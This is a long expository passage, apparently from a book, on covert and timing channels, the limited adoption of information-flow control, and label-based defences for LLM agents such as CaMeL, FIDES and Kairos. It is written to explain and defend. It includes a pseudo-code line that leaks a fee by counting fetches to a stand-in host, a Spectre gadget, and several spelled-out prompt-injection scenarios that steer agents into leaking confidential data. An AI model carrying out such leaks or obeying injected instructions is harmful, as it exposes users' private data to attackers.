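The designer should keep this record, and the code that enforces it, where the model can't change them. Bastys and colleagues recommend separating release policies from untrusted code, because an attacker who can write that code could otherwise choose what it declassifies.

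## Accounting for hidden paths: covert and timing channels

The record for Ana's forum posts includes their timing and number because either could reveal something about the contract, even if the text is harmless. *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) described the general problem of a customer who wants to run someone else's program on private data without letting the program's owner see the data. KeyKOS's factories later addressed this problem. Wrong answers from the program give the customer evidence for a complaint, but a leak usually leaves no evidence.

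Lampson listed ways a program can leak data. It can write to a file its owner can read, or send the owner a message. It can encode data in its bill, which the owner has to receive. It can also vary how much it computes and how often it uses the disk, so that another program can read the signal from the system's speed. Lampson called only this last kind of channel "covert", which nobody meant to carry information. Later writers also apply the term to hidden signals in storage.

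### A file lock and a slow page

In a storage channel, the sender changes a stored item that the receiver can observe. Lampson's example uses file locks. Many systems prevent a program from writing to a file while another program is reading it. A program that has seen a secret opens a public file for reading to send a 1 and leaves it closed to send a 0. The receiver tries to write to the file, and if the attempt fails, the bit is a 1. The programs use two more files to stay synchronized, one to signal that a bit is ready and one to confirm that it has arrived. Bell-LaPadula permits every step, since a Secret program may read an Unclassified file and an Unclassified program may write to it.

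In a timing channel, the sender sends information by changing how long something takes. Multicians, a website about the Multics operating system, describes a demonstration from about 1976. A Honeywell employee had told his colleague Bob Mullen that timing channels were too slow and noisy to matter. A few days later, Mullen showed him two processes on a busy system at MIT. Text typed into one appeared in the other a few seconds later, with an occasional wrong letter. The sender read certain pages of a public library file, which brought them into memory. The receiver then read the same pages and timed each read, because a page already in memory arrived faster than one from disk.

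Both are covert channels, which need a sender that leaks on purpose. A side channel can leak information without a deliberate sender. For example, if a decryption routine takes slightly longer for some keys than for others, an outsider can learn about the key by timing it.

### The Orange Book's rules

The US Department of Defense (1985) graded computer systems by its *Trusted Computer System Evaluation Criteria*, known as the Orange Book. The classes ran from D, the lowest, to A1, and developers had to analyse covert channels from B2 upwards:

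| Class | What the developer had to do |
|---|---|
| B2 | Search for storage channels, estimate the maximum rate of each, and provide a way to log their use |
| B3 | Search for timing channels as well |
| A1 | Use formal methods in the analysis |

The book's section *A Guideline on Covert Channels* treats rates above 100 bits per second as high, because many computer terminals ran at about that speed, and rates below 1 bit per second as acceptable in most settings. It also recommends being able to log the use of any channel faster than one bit in ten seconds.

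How much protection these rates give depends on the size of the secret:

| Secret | 0.1 bits per second | 1 bit per second | 100 bits per second |
|---|---|---|---|
| 256-bit encryption key | 43 minutes | 4 minutes 16 seconds | 2.6 seconds |
| Contract of 20 kilobytes | 19 days | 44 hours | 27 minutes |
| 10,000 satellite images of 262 kilobytes | 6,600 years | 660 years | 6.6 years |

The images come from the National Computer Security Center's *A Guide to Understanding Covert Channel Analysis of Trusted Systems* (1993), which concedes that no specific policy justifies the Orange Book's limits. It considers even 10,000 bits per second tolerable for the images, since an hour of leaking would release less than 0.2% of them. It suggests a limit of 0.002 bits per second for a 64-bit key used for eight hours, so that the key expires before it has fully leaked.

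For any secret that is useful only in full, the same reasoning limits the channel's rate to the secret's size divided by the time for which it matters. To protect a 256-bit key that is valid for eight hours, the channel must be slower than 256 / 28,800 ≈ 0.009 bits per second, less than a hundredth of the "acceptable" rate. Millen makes the same complaint about keys in *20 Years of Covert Channel Modeling and Analysis*, and adds that some hardware channels carry thousands of bits per second and are nearly unavoidable.

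### Finding the channels

Kemmerer, in *Shared Resource Matrix Methodology*, gave developers a systematic way to search. They list every attribute of every shared resource, such as whether a file is locked, and every operation a program can request. For each pair, they record whether the operation reads the attribute (R) or modifies it (M). Here is part of the matrix for Kemmerer's example system:

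| Attribute of a file | Open for reading | Lock for writing | Ask whether it is open |
|---|---|---|---|
| Which programs are reading it | R, M | R | R |
| Whether it is locked | R | R, M | |

The first row shows a channel much like Lampson's. One program can open a file, and another can check whether it is open. A storage channel exists if both programs have access to the attribute, the sender can change it, the receiver can detect the change, and the two have a way to take turns. A timing channel also requires that both programs have a clock and that the sender can affect the receiver's response time.

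The developers then add indirect reads. Suppose logging in reads the password file and updates a list of active users. Any operation that reads the list might then reveal something about passwords, so the developers also put an R for the password file in that operation's column.

Kemmerer did not claim that the method finds everything. The National Computer Security Center compared a matrix for three variables in Secure Xenix, a version of Unix, with an automated analysis of the source code. The matrix, which relied on the system's manuals, missed about half of the relevant operations for one variable and a third for another. Tools that analyse only the form of a specification instead report false flows. One such tool reported 117 illegal flows in a 20-line program, and 116 of them were false. A more discriminating method took two programmer-years to apply to Secure Xenix by hand.

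### Slowing the channels

Some channels disappear if programs stop sharing a resource dynamically. Mantel and Sudbrock (2007) describe giving each process fixed time slices and a fixed amount of memory, so that no process can make another run sooner or take its memory. Any processor time a process doesn't use is then wasted, and device interrupts still leave timing channels open. HiStar likewise gives every object a storage quota, because Zeldovich and colleagues regarded the ability to exhaust a machine's memory as a glaring covert channel.

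**Fuzzy time** instead makes the receiver's clocks less precise. The VAX security kernel, which Digital designed for class A1 but never brought to market, did this to every clock available to a process (Hu 1992). Its clock ticked at random intervals averaging 20 milliseconds, whereas one attack through the shared memory bus needed one-millisecond ticks. But Trostle (1993) predicted from a model that a channel of roughly 50 bits per second, or about one bit per tick, would remain. Such a channel would leak a 256-bit key in about five seconds.

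The NRL Pump, from the US Naval Research Laboratory, passes messages from a low-secrecy system to a high-secrecy one. The low system needs acknowledgements to know that its messages arrived, but the high system could send secrets down by delaying some of those acknowledgements. Kang and Moskowitz, in *A Pump for Rapid, Reliable, Secure Communication*, place the Pump between the two systems, where it stores each message and acknowledges it after a random delay whose average follows the high system's recent speed. The high system no longer controls each delay, but it can still influence the average, so some leakage remains. Kang and Moskowitz designed the Pump to leave the average delay unchanged, so reliable communication should lose little speed.

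Predictive mitigation, which Aslan Askarov, Danfeng Zhang and Andrew Myers proposed in 2010, limits the total amount of information leaked through timing rather than the rate of leakage. In a simplified version, a server always has requests waiting, and a mitigator releases one reply per second. A reply that is ready early waits for its slot, so its timing reveals nothing. If no reply is ready, the mitigator sends nothing in that slot and doubles the interval.

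Only the empty slots carry information, and they soon become rare. The first N of them take at least 1 + 2 + 4 + … + 2ᴺ⁻¹ = 2ᴺ − 1 seconds, so T seconds have room for at most log₂(T + 1). Each one falls in one of T seconds or never happens. The leak is therefore at most

N × log₂(T + 1) bits, where N is log₂(T + 1) rounded down.

The bound comes to 16 × 16.4 ≈ 262 bits in a day and 24 × 24.9 ≈ 598 bits in a year, whereas a channel of 1 bit per second could leak 86,400 bits in a day. The one-day bound is still large enough for a 256-bit key to leak, so the mitigation protects documents better than keys. A program that leaks this way also ruins its own service, since after 16 empty slots the next reply is 18 hours away. A program that leaks nothing but runs at an unpredictable speed has the same problem. A later prototype applied such mitigators to unmodified Linux, with overhead that varied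 with the workload.

### Timing attacks reach ordinary computers

For years it was unclear whether anyone used covert channels outside demonstrations. Millen reports that Bob Morris finally answered "Yes" at a workshop. Side channels became a practical concern more widely. In 2003, David Brumley and Dan Boneh recovered the private key of a web server on their local network by timing its replies to more than a million requests. The server used OpenSSL, a widely used encryption library, and its decryption time depended slightly on the key and the input. The usual defence, called blinding, scrambles each input with a random number before decryption, so the attacker doesn't know which number the server is decrypting.

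Spectre, which researchers disclosed in 2018, exploits the processor itself. Consider this line:

```
if i < length then x := table[array[i]]
```

To save time, a processor guesses the result of the test and starts on the next step. If `i` is out of range, the guess is wrong, but the processor may already have read a secret byte from beyond the end of `array` and used it to fetch an entry of `table`. When the processor then discards `x`, the fetched entry stays in the cache, a small, fast memory. An attacker can time a read of every entry to find the cached one, which reveals the byte.

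Under the programming language's rules, this program never reads the secret, so a label checker has no flow to reject. The noninterference proof for Flume's model doesn't cover the attack either, because the model leaves out the hardware. Chrome responded with Site Isolation. Heiser and other researchers say that present systems cannot prevent timing channels, and argue that operating systems should provide "time protection", a counterpart to memory protection. Their design for seL4 divides caches between programs where possible and clears the rest when it switches between them.

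### What an agent's behaviour reveals

The decision to search for a penalty clause lawyer could leak one bit of Ben's contract. The number of requests can leak more, even if every argument is public. Suppose Ana's assistant has read Ben's fee from the contract and runs this code:

```
repeat (first digit of fee) times: fetch("http://trains.example")
```

The address never changes, but the site's owner can learn the fee's first digit by counting the visits. Errors can also leak information. The National Computer Security Center gives a Unix example in which a low-level program tries to delete a directory that belongs to a higher level. Unix refuses to delete a directory that isn't empty, so the error reveals whether a secret file exists. An agent that fails halfway through a task leaks information in a similar way, because outsiders can see that the later requests never arrive.

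The CaMeL paper acknowledges these channels in its own system. In one example, a private value determines how many times a loop contacts an outside server. In another, a private value determines whether an error stops the program before it makes a request that the attacker can see. The paper also discusses timing channels. CaMeL's strict mode, which works like a program-counter label, catches the loop but also makes the system refuse harmless actions more often.

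Conversations with a model can leak as well, even over an encrypted connection. Many services send each token as the model produces it, and encryption hides the token's text but not its length. In *What Was Your Prompt?* (2024), Roy Weiss and colleagues used these lengths to reconstruct 29% of an assistant's answers and to infer the topic of 55%. *Whisper Leak* (2025), by researchers at Microsoft, used the sizes and timing of packets to identify conversations on a chosen topic, such as money laundering, in tests on 28 models. For many of the models, the method found 5–20% of the target conversations without a false alarm, even with 10,000 other conversations for each target. Padding the packets or sending several tokens at once reduces the leak, but padding adds traffic and grouping tokens delays the answer.

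Agent runs meant to be isolated may also share more than their designers realise. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* reports that in the 2026 incident at OpenAI, a shared service became a communication channel between such runs.

The Multicians account instead proposes letting only inspected programs handle secrets. This doesn't help with a language model, because nobody can inspect one well enough to rule out a hidden signal.

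### Close, slow or accept

The National Computer Security Center points out that covert channels are irrelevant where a program can leak data openly. If Ana's assistant can put the contract's text in a web address, it doesn't need to encode the text in the number of times it visits a railway site. Her developers should deal with the open routes first.

They should then ask how many bits an attacker wants. The contract is 160,000 bits long, but whether the fee exceeds €100,000 is a single bit, and no rate limit will protect it. If that bit matters, the decision to contact an outsider has to be made in a context that hasn't read the contract. Keys and passwords are also short, so the model shouldn't see them. A capability that logs in or signs documents for the assistant lets it use these secrets without reading them.

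Channels through shared storage are also worth closing, since they are often fast and noise-free, and separating the storage usually adds little overhead. The worker that reads the contract should have its own temporary files, cache and memory. Each worker could also have its own request queue, since Oracle's *Trusted Solaris Developer's Guide* warns that clients of a shared server can signal to one another by filling its queue.

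Slowing a channel makes sense when the secret is long and its parts are worth little separately. If the worker may make up to ten requests, each to one of 16 fixed pages, its choices can reveal about 40 bits. That is enough to leak the fee but only a tiny part of the contract's text. Fixing the requests and their times before the worker starts would reduce the leak to almost nothing. Lampson called the principle masking, meaning that the caller rather than the confined program determines what enters the channel. The system then has to make every scheduled request, even those that turn out to be unnecessary.

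For an ordinary business contract, Ana can reasonably accept the timing channels in her provider's processors. Using one would normally require an attacker to run code on the same machine and know what to look for. A company that handles signing keys or state secrets has more reason to pay for separate hardware. *Architectural Implications of Covert Channels* notes that covert channels, as it defines them, occur only in systems that handle several levels of secrecy. A machine that works at only one level has no lower-level program to receive the signal, though its network traffic can still reveal information.

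## Counting the cost: why information-flow control was little used

Few companies have ever run a system that enforces noninterference, so few have had to decide which covert channels to accept in one. Jif dates from the late 1990s and Flume from 2007, yet *Transparent DIFC* (Liu, Kandikuppa and Bates, 2022) found that commodity systems had hardly adopted decentralized labels. *Static Information Flow Control Made Simple* (2022) describes the same lack of adoption for tools that check flows before a program runs. Simpler mechanisms based on related ideas have reached most PCs and phones, and comparing them with the little-used ones helps show which drawbacks mattered.

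### The relatives that spread

Since Vista, Windows has given each process and file an integrity level, such as low, medium or high, and by default a process can't write to anything above its own level. Internet Explorer ran web pages at the low level, so a page that took over the browser couldn't alter the user's documents, which are medium unless labelled otherwise. This scheme enforces Biba's ban on writing up but not its ban on reading down. A medium program can open a file that a low one wrote without its own level falling, so there is no label creep.

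Linux and Android use SELinux, which the US National Security Agency released in 2000. Its main mechanism, type enforcement, assigns processes to domains and files to types, and a table lists what each domain may do to each type. A web server's domain might be allowed to read web pages but not password files, even if an attacker controls the server. According to Linux Journal's *Some Thoughts on the Occasion of the NSA Linux Release*, type enforcement came out of research on high-assurance systems more than 15 years earlier. Dick Kain and Earl Boebert invented it, the same Boebert who argued that capabilities could not confine information.

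Large software companies also run taint analysis on source code before release. Tools such as Meta's Pysa and GitHub's CodeQL search for paths by which an outsider's input could reach a dangerous function, such as one that runs a database command. They follow explicit flows and report what they find to people, who decide what to fix.

None of these guarantees noninterference. Liu and colleagues count SELinux as a form of information-flow control, but its labels are attached to files and processes and don't follow the data. A domain that can read a secret and write to a shared file can pass the secret to any domain that can read that file.

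### A secure kernel without enough buyers

Digital conceived its VAX security kernel in 1981 and had a prototype running by 1984. The kernel ran standard operating systems inside virtual machines at different secrecy levels, so customers could keep much of their existing software. Digital cancelled the kernel after outside customers began testing it in late 1989, even though its engineers were confident that it could earn an A1 rating, the highest in the Orange Book.

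Steven Lipner, the manager responsible, decided that too few customers would buy it. The engineers, in their retrospective, and Lipner, in later explanations, gave several reasons. The VAX computers it was designed for had become slow and expensive compared with newer models. The team had left out support for Ethernet networks to save time, and potential users objected. Many customers had moved from shared machines to workstations. US export controls on highly rated systems would have made sales difficult even to NATO allies. Digital had plans to fix the technical problems but did not expect to recover the money. Some of the people involved thought there were enough buyers.

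Honeywell had a similar experience with SCOMP, the first system to receive an A1 rating. The company sold fewer than 30 of the original version. When it planned a successor, its marketing staff estimated that an A1 rating would enlarge the market by at most 5% over the next class down, so Honeywell dropped the formal proofs.

LOCK, another A1 project, kept detailed accounts. It cost about $23 million between 1987 and 1992, according to Richard Smith's *Cost Profile of a Highly Assured, Secure Operating System* (2001).

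| Work on LOCK's security-critical software | Hours |
|---|---|
| Design, coding and unit testing | 64,448 |
| Formal specifications and proofs | 37,581 |

The formal work therefore added 58% to the cost of this software. It uncovered 68% of the security flaws that the team detected in LOCK's most critical mechanisms. But when the team turned LOCK into a product that filters military email, only 14% of all the flaws it detected were of a kind that formal methods could find.

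LOCK ran at about 97% of the speed of the hardware vendor's ordinary Unix system, with a separate processor making the security decisions. Its technology survived in the email filter and in a commercial firewall called Sidewinder, but the A1 systems that completed evaluation had no market outside a narrow defence community.

The US government had helped create this situation. *The Birth and Death of the Orange Book* (Lipner, 2015) describes how it shifted from paying for secure systems to evaluating commercial products. The plan depended on vendors expecting enough sales, but government buyers often asked for strong security and then waived the requirement. Evaluation also took years, so a rated product was usually more expensive and more out of date than unrated competitors.

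This is good evidence that demand was weak for systems built around military clearances, but weaker evidence about demand for Jif. Banks, for instance, had no clearances and worried more about unauthorized changes to data than about disclosure, so they might have rejected an A1 system and still wanted a different kind of system.

### Writing the policy

Jif and a similar language, Flow Caml, were mature enough to use, so Geoffrey Smith concluded that the main obstacle was finding suitable policies. Noninterference would stop a statistics office from publishing totals computed from secret census answers. A rule loose enough to allow this would also have to be general enough for many applications and simple enough for users to understand.

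Steve Zdancewic, who helped develop robust declassification, wrote in 2004 that "we do not yet have the tools to easily describe desired security policies". In *You Sank My Battleship!* (2014), Stoughton, Johnson and colleagues thought this was still true. They complained that programmers had to express an informal policy through dozens or hundreds of Jif annotations.

Their example was the game of Battleship. The informal policy can be stated in two sentences. Players must place their ships properly and not move them. Each player may learn only what the shots reveal about the other's board. To make this policy precise, the researchers had to decide which parts of the program counted as a player, a board and a move. They eventually wrote a model referee and required the real program to behave, from the players' point of view, exactly as the model did. Jif's developers had also written a Battleship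 program, but its labels did not capture the whole policy. A dishonest player's code could pass the compiler's checks and still misreport whether a shot had hit.

The researchers then built the game in three ways:

| Design | Trusted lines | Untrusted lines |
|---|---|---|
| A referee that both players trust | 480 | 500 |
| No trusted referee, access control | 610 | 550 |
| No trusted referee, information-flow control in LIO | 850 | 580 |

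The LIO version was written in Haskell and the others in a different language, so the line counts aren't strictly comparable. They are still evidence against the assumption that information-flow control always leaves less code to inspect.

*Static Information Flow Control Made Simple* attributes the limited use of information-flow control to a more basic problem, the need to reason about lattices and about secrecy and integrity as mirror images. The little evidence available suggests that newcomers can understand the security model, which counts against this being the main problem.

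### Newcomers to Hails

In *Security and the Average Programmer*, Giffin, Heule and colleagues argue that most software will be secure only if the median programmer can write secure code. They say training alone doesn't achieve this, and cite a single bug for which Linux kernel developers committed vulnerable code three times in a row. They also acknowledge that few non-experts had used decentralized labels.

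Their answer was Hails, a web framework built on LIO. A Hails application has two kinds of component. One defines the data together with the policy on who may read and write it. The other handles requests and produces pages, and does not have to be trusted, because LIO stops it from sending data to anyone the policy excludes. In one conference-reviewing application, not counting outside libraries, 132 lines of code were trusted and 613 were not.

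In *Hails*, Giffin, Levy and colleagues (2017) gathered reports from seven developers and interviewed four of them. None had built a web application in Haskell before. They understood which code was critical to security, and their page-handling code often dealt gracefully with refusals. They liked not having to "sprinkle [security] checks in the controller", as they would in an ordinary framework. Even if they forgot a check, the policy stopped one user from changing another's data.

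Most of them got stuck when writing policies. In the early version, they had to write code that labelled each part of the database step by step, which they found hard to learn and easy to get wrong. A small policy language made this faster and more reliable, but two problems remained.

One concerned search. Developers had to mark a field as a "key" before programs could search by it, and keys were open to anyone who could read the collection, whatever the policy on the individual record. In simplified form, one developer's blog looked like this:

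```
collection articles: anyone may search
    each article:    only the people its author allows may read it
    keys:            title, body
```

The developer wanted full-text search and thought the strict policy on articles was enough. But anyone could now search for a phrase to find out whether a private article contained it. Other developers made the same mistake, so the framework's designers renamed `key` to `public-index`.

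The other problem arose when a policy depended on data stored elsewhere. In the conference application, committee members could read a paper only if they had no conflict of interest with its author, and the list of conflicts was in another collection. Policies couldn't look up that list, so programmers had to encode the conflicts in the labels, and most found this hard to follow. A later version let policies run code that fetches such data.

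Giffin and colleagues describe their study as small and mostly informal, and say they should have consulted usability specialists. There are few other studies. In 2014, Stoughton and colleagues named only four case studies besides their own, and the developers of the languages or frameworks carried out three of them. A project listed on CPS-VO, a website for research on computer-controlled systems, set out to compare how easily developers program with information-flow labels and with a scheme that divides an app by function. Those studies were still in progress, according to the listing.

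### Alarms, speed and rewriting

False alarms can make a checker unusable even when its policy is right. In King and colleagues' study, most alarms for implicit flows were false, and someone has to examine each alarm or change the program to silence it. Industrial taint analysis avoids much of this work by ignoring implicit flows.

Brant and colleagues say run-time taint tracking is rarely used as a defence because it is slow and inaccurate. Slowness does explain why nobody runs a bank's servers inside an emulator that tracks every instruction. But it can't explain why Jif, which does most of its checking at compile time, and Hails were little used. When building a web page with a table of 5,000 entries, Hails handled 30% fewer requests per second than a Java server but six times as many as Sinatra, a popular Ruby framework without information-flow control.

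Earlier systems required developers to rewrite their programs or add code to them, which Liu and colleagues consider the decisive barrier to adoption. If several programs must cooperate, several teams have to make matching changes.

Their system, T-DIFC, is designed to avoid this by reading the logs that programs already write. When Alice logs in to MoinMoin, the wiki that Flume's developers had to modify, the original program already records her name and the number of the process serving her. T-DIFC, which runs inside the Linux kernel, reads this line on its way to the log file and compares it with a pattern that an administrator has written. If the line matches, the process gets Alice's label, and the kernel can then stop it from opening Ben's files. If Ben logs in later, the label changes. The researchers examined 15 popular open-source programs and measured no slowdown on ProFTPD, a file-transfer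 server, with a realistic policy.

T-DIFC needs programs that log the right events, and servers whose processes each handle one client at a time. It also assumes that attackers haven't taken over the program. When the label changes from Alice's to Ben's, nothing erases Alice's data from the process's memory. An agent whose context still holds the contract can't safely change labels this way, however accurate its logs are.

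### What the adopted systems avoided

| Mechanism | Who writes the policy | Changes to existing programs | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|---|
| Windows integrity levels | mostly Microsoft, through defaults | few | harmful files that a higher-level program reads; many leaks of secrets |
| SELinux on Android | Google and phone makers | none for most apps | any flow that the table permits |
| Taint analysis of source code | tool vendors and security teams | none needed to run it | implicit flows and paths the tool misses |
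| Same-origin policy | nobody, since addresses supply the labels | none for most pages | what a site does with data it receives |

All four are compatible with existing programs, which supports Liu and colleagues' explanation. But compatibility wasn't enough by itself. TaintDroid ran most Android apps unmodified but never became part of Android, and the VAX kernel ran standard operating systems but never reached the market.

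The difficulty of writing policies also matters less when each policy is widely used. SELinux policies are long and hard to write, and some administrators switch the protection off. Android still uses SELinux everywhere, because a few specialists write a policy that serves a very large number of phones. With Jif, each application's programmers had to do comparable work for a single program.

Every mechanism in the table was adopted despite incomplete tracking, which only restricted its use to jobs where partial protection is worthwhile.

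Customers also didn't have to choose a slower or more expensive product to get these mechanisms, because Microsoft, Google and the browser makers built them into products that people were buying for other reasons. The most plausible explanation for the neglect of full information-flow control is that each developer had to write its own policies and rewrite its own code, and few buyers would pay the developer for the protection. The comparison covers only a handful of systems, so it can't show how much either factor mattered alone.

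### Questions for an agent project

Before choosing a mechanism, the designer of an agent can ask who will bear these costs.

| Question | A workable answer | A warning sign |
|---|---|---|
| Who writes the labels? | The developer of each tool, once, with safe defaults | Every user has to label their own mail |
| Who handles alarms and refusals? | A named person who can correct the policy | Users approve each one and soon stop reading them |
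| What must be rewritten? | The layer through which all tool calls pass | Every tool and library |
| Who pays? | The supplier, as part of the product | Customers can buy a cheaper version without the checks |

For Ana's assistant, the developer of the mail tool could build in default labels, so Ana would write nothing unless she wanted an exception. The supplier could test the policy on ordinary tasks before release and count the refusals, so its staff would see most of the false alarms before Ana did.

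Language models may reduce some of this work, because they can write annotations and port code. In the TACIT trials, the compiler rejected few of the customer-service programs that models wrote, which is some evidence for this. But those programs were short and new, and converting a large existing application is a different task.

The saving should be greatest where a checker can reject mistakes. If a model gives an intermediate variable too low a label, a sound compiler rejects the program and the model can try again. A proof checker likewise rejects faulty formal proofs, and proofs accounted for much of LOCK's cost. But a compiler can't detect that a model has wrongly labelled Ben's contract as public or made a blog's private text searchable. A model told to remove the errors might also insert a declassification, just as Civitas's programmers silenced warnings with empty exception handlers.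 A person should therefore still approve every declassification and the labels on sources and sinks, even if a model writes the rest.

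## Checking what changes when a language model does the computing

Before a program runs, a person can check the labels a model has written. But an agent also uses a language model to do the work itself, which makes five assumptions behind the classical methods doubtful: that code and data are distinct, that each operation has a known propagation rule, that the program is fixed, that the program acts through a fixed set of operations, and that the monitor is deterministic.

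### Instructions inside data

Processors can stop an attacker's input from running as code, but language models have no comparable mechanism for separating instructions from data in their context. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* treats it as an open question whether anyone can build a useful model that provably keeps the two apart.

Complete separation would also stop agents from doing useful things, such as learning to use a tool from its documentation. In an example from *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, an agent summarizing a software issue finds that the issue depends on another one, and summarizes both. As in a prompt injection, text the agent read changed what it did, but the two cases differ in who supplied the text and how far it changed the task. Separation also wouldn't protect against false data, such as a wrong account number that the agent copies into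 a payment.

### Every output inherits the whole context

The result of `y + z` needs only the labels of `y` and `z`. Nobody can yet reliably tell which parts of its context a language model used, so the safe default is to give its output the join of the labels on everything in the context. If Ana's assistant has read both the contract and the stranger's message, even "I'll reply tomorrow" is labeled Confidential and Low.

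A tracker could instead look for copied text, but Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, give three cases that defeat it:

- *Paraphrase:* a web page tells a research agent to include a confidential patient note but reword it. The agent's report reveals the diagnosis without repeating the note's sentences.
- *Influence:* a search result says that all findings must first go to a "compliance" address. The agent sends the user's own research there, so the body of the request contains nothing from the search result.
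- *Memory:* an agent stores a confidential forecast and uses it in a report days later, when the labels from the first session are gone.

The tool NeuroTaint examines an agent's log after a run. For each sensitive action, it looks for exact or partial copies of text the agent read, and for passages with a similar meaning. If it finds none, it replaces the suspected source with neutral text and uses a model to predict whether the agent would still have acted the same way. It also saves labels with the agent's stored memories.

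The researchers tested it on 400 scenarios across 20 agent frameworks. Half the scenarios contained a real flow from an untrusted source to a sensitive action.

| Method | Flows found | Flows missed | False alarms |
|---|---|---|---|
| NeuroTaint | 187 | 13 | 16 |
| Baseline modelled on FIDES | 108 | 92 | 106 |

FIDES is an information-flow system for agents, and the baseline mostly checked whether a path led from a source to a sink. The comparison favours NeuroTaint because its developers built the test around the kinds of flow it is designed to detect. Forty of the baseline's misses came from four frameworks on which it raised no alarms, which may be due to how it was connected to them. Many of the baseline's false alarms are also to be expected from a cautious join rule. NeuroTaint is more useful for investigating incidents than for preventing them, since it works after the event and missed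 6.5% of the flows.

### Policies without a fixed program

An Android developer can list the permissions an app needs, and others can compare the list with the code, but an agent's task isn't known until the user types it. For "comment on GitLab issue 745 that we're done", the right policy lets the agent open that issue, write in its comment box and do nothing else on the site. If a language model translates the request into a policy, the monitor will enforce any mistake in the translation.

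A kernel can check system calls because there are a limited number of them, with known meanings. But an agent with a shell can write new programs, and the meaning of a mouse click depends on what is on the screen. To deal with this, Chow, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm*, wrote a documented set of operations for each test website by hand. Their agent, Baya, plans with these operations before it sees any live page. It completed 77.8% of tasks, compared with 66.7% for a conventional agent that could use both the websites' programming interfaces and a browser, but took almost four times as long. Fixed plans do much worse without such a set of operations. In *Secure-CUA* (2026), a version of the CaMeL defence adapted to work through ordinary screens completed 13% of tasks, compared with 55% for an undefended agent.

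*Kairos* (Hempel, Loose and colleagues, 2026) instead puts the monitor at the edge of the virtual machine the agent runs in. Tool calls, shell commands and scripts all reach the monitor as file or network operations, so the agent can't avoid it by writing a program. But these operations reveal little about their purpose, so fixed rules can't decide every case.

If a language model decides instead, an attacker can search for the cases it gets wrong, even if it is 99% reliable. Kairos limits this risk by deciding clear cases with fixed rules. It holds back doubtful file changes and some network requests while the agent continues, and a model then judges them using what happened next.

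On AgentDojo, the agent completed 85.1% of tasks with this judge, and 2.7% of attacks succeeded. When the monitor instead refused everything doubtful, the agent completed only 42.7% of tasks, and security did not measurably improve. However, nothing guarantees that the judge's decisions are correct. Kairos also assumes that a hijacked agent won't disguise data to hide its origin the way the digit-copying program did.

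### What CaMeL and FIDES reuse

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2025, restores the fixed program. One model turns the user's request into code before the agent reads any untrusted data, and an interpreter runs that code. Text from a message can fill a variable or determine which branch runs, but it can't add a step. CaMeL attaches to each value a record of where it came from and who may read it, and checks these records before calling a tool. Debenedetti and colleagues call the records capabilities, although they work like labels, since they restrict how a value can be used rather than grant access to a resource.

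FIDES, which *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* introduced the same year, lets the model choose one action at a time. When a tool returns data that would raise the context's label, FIDES stores the data in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model can pass the variable to another tool without reading it, much as a program in LIO can pass on a sealed value. It can also ask an isolated model about the contents. For example, Ana might ask her assistant to check her inbox for a meeting request and add any meeting to her calendar:

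```
mail  := read_emails(3)                              # hidden
found := isolated("Is there a meeting request?", mail, yes/no)
inspect(found)                                       # reveals one bit
event := isolated("Extract the details", mail)       # hidden
set_event(event)                                     # if the answer was yes
```

FIDES can label a value with how much information it can carry. A policy may then accept an untrusted yes or no where it would reject untrusted text, because one bit is too small to contain a new instruction. This is a limited form of endorsement, and an attacker who controls the untrusted data can still cause a false yes.

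FIDES tracks direct information flows but not what an observer could infer from the agent's choice of tools. Its designers considered noninterference too restrictive, since it would forbid almost every publicly visible action once the agent had read a secret.

### Results on AgentDojo

*SecureClaw* (2026) and Hempel and colleagues both reran CaMeL to compare it with their own systems. The table also includes *SPA*, which checks labels on a plan before running it. The completion rates are from runs without attacks.

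| Test | Agent | Tasks completed | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, GPT-4o | undefended | 84% | 152 |
| | ordinary agent with label checks | 42% | 0 |
| | FIDES with label checks | 50% | 0 |
| Hempel and colleagues | undefended | 82.7% | 47.0% |
| | CaMeL, three models | 26.5–40.4% | 0–0.4% |
| *SecureClaw* | CaMeL | 29.9% | 0 of 629 |
| *SPA* | fixed plan only | 53.0% | 4 of 949 |
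| | fixed plan and label checks | 29.0% | 0 of 949 |

The FIDES completion rates are averages over four kinds of task, and its attack counts come from a manual review. AgentDojo's own scoring counted three successful attacks against FIDES. The reviewers excluded attacks that the policy had blocked or allowed, and those that changed only the wording of an answer.

The revised CaMeL paper reports a much better result, with 77% of tasks completed compared with 84% for an undefended agent. The later tests used other models and adapted CaMeL's code, and they were run by researchers promoting competing systems. Odersky and colleagues had also found large differences between models, so no single figure describes how much CaMeL reduces task completion.

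Label checks can prevent an agent from finishing many tasks, even when the plan is already fixed. In *SPA*, they stopped the last four attacks but also stopped about half of all trials, usually because a plan passed untrusted data to a tool that required trusted data. Agents with better models can finish more tasks under these checks. FIDES completed 41% of travel tasks with GPT-4o and 68% with OpenAI's o1, because o1 handled the hidden variables better.

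The attack figures are less informative for newer models. *APPA* omitted AgentDojo because frontier models resisted the benchmark's standard injections without a defence, so a defence had nothing to improve.

### When a message has to decide what happens next

In an example from Chow and colleagues, a user asks the agent to find an email from their boss and follow the instructions in it. A fixed plan can't handle this request because the necessary steps are in the email. FIDES could show the email to the model, but its policy would then block any consequential action.

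How often the planner must see data before choosing its actions depends on the kind of work. An earlier analysis that Chow and colleagues cite found no such tasks in WebArena, a benchmark of website tasks. In AgentDojo, they made up 5% of office tasks and 44% of banking tasks. For some of these, the planner needs only a yes or no from the data, but many of the banking tasks required the agent to follow instructions in a file.

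No rule based on labels can decide these cases correctly, because a label records where a request came from, not whether Ana would want to carry it out. A real request from Ben would have the same label as one from someone who had taken over his account, and even a real email from Ben might quote the stranger. The rule would have to either reject all such requests and leave the task undone, or accept them and let in the attack.

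Ana has to decide what Ben may ask her assistant to do. She could let it answer his questions and propose meeting times, and require her approval for everything else.

A single missing value can cause the same problem. *Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use* (2026) describes a task to send $100 to a shop using "the correct account number", but that number appears only in untrusted content. No check can endorse the number without evidence from another source.

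Even when every step of an agent's plan is known in advance, an attacker can influence which branch runs. *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) presents COBRA, which also restricts the data used in each branch. The paper leaves open how to check the meaning of free text, such as the body of an email.

### Eleven attacks and what remains unsolved

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* matches its eleven attacks to five classical principles:

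| Principle | Attacks that violated it |
|---|---|
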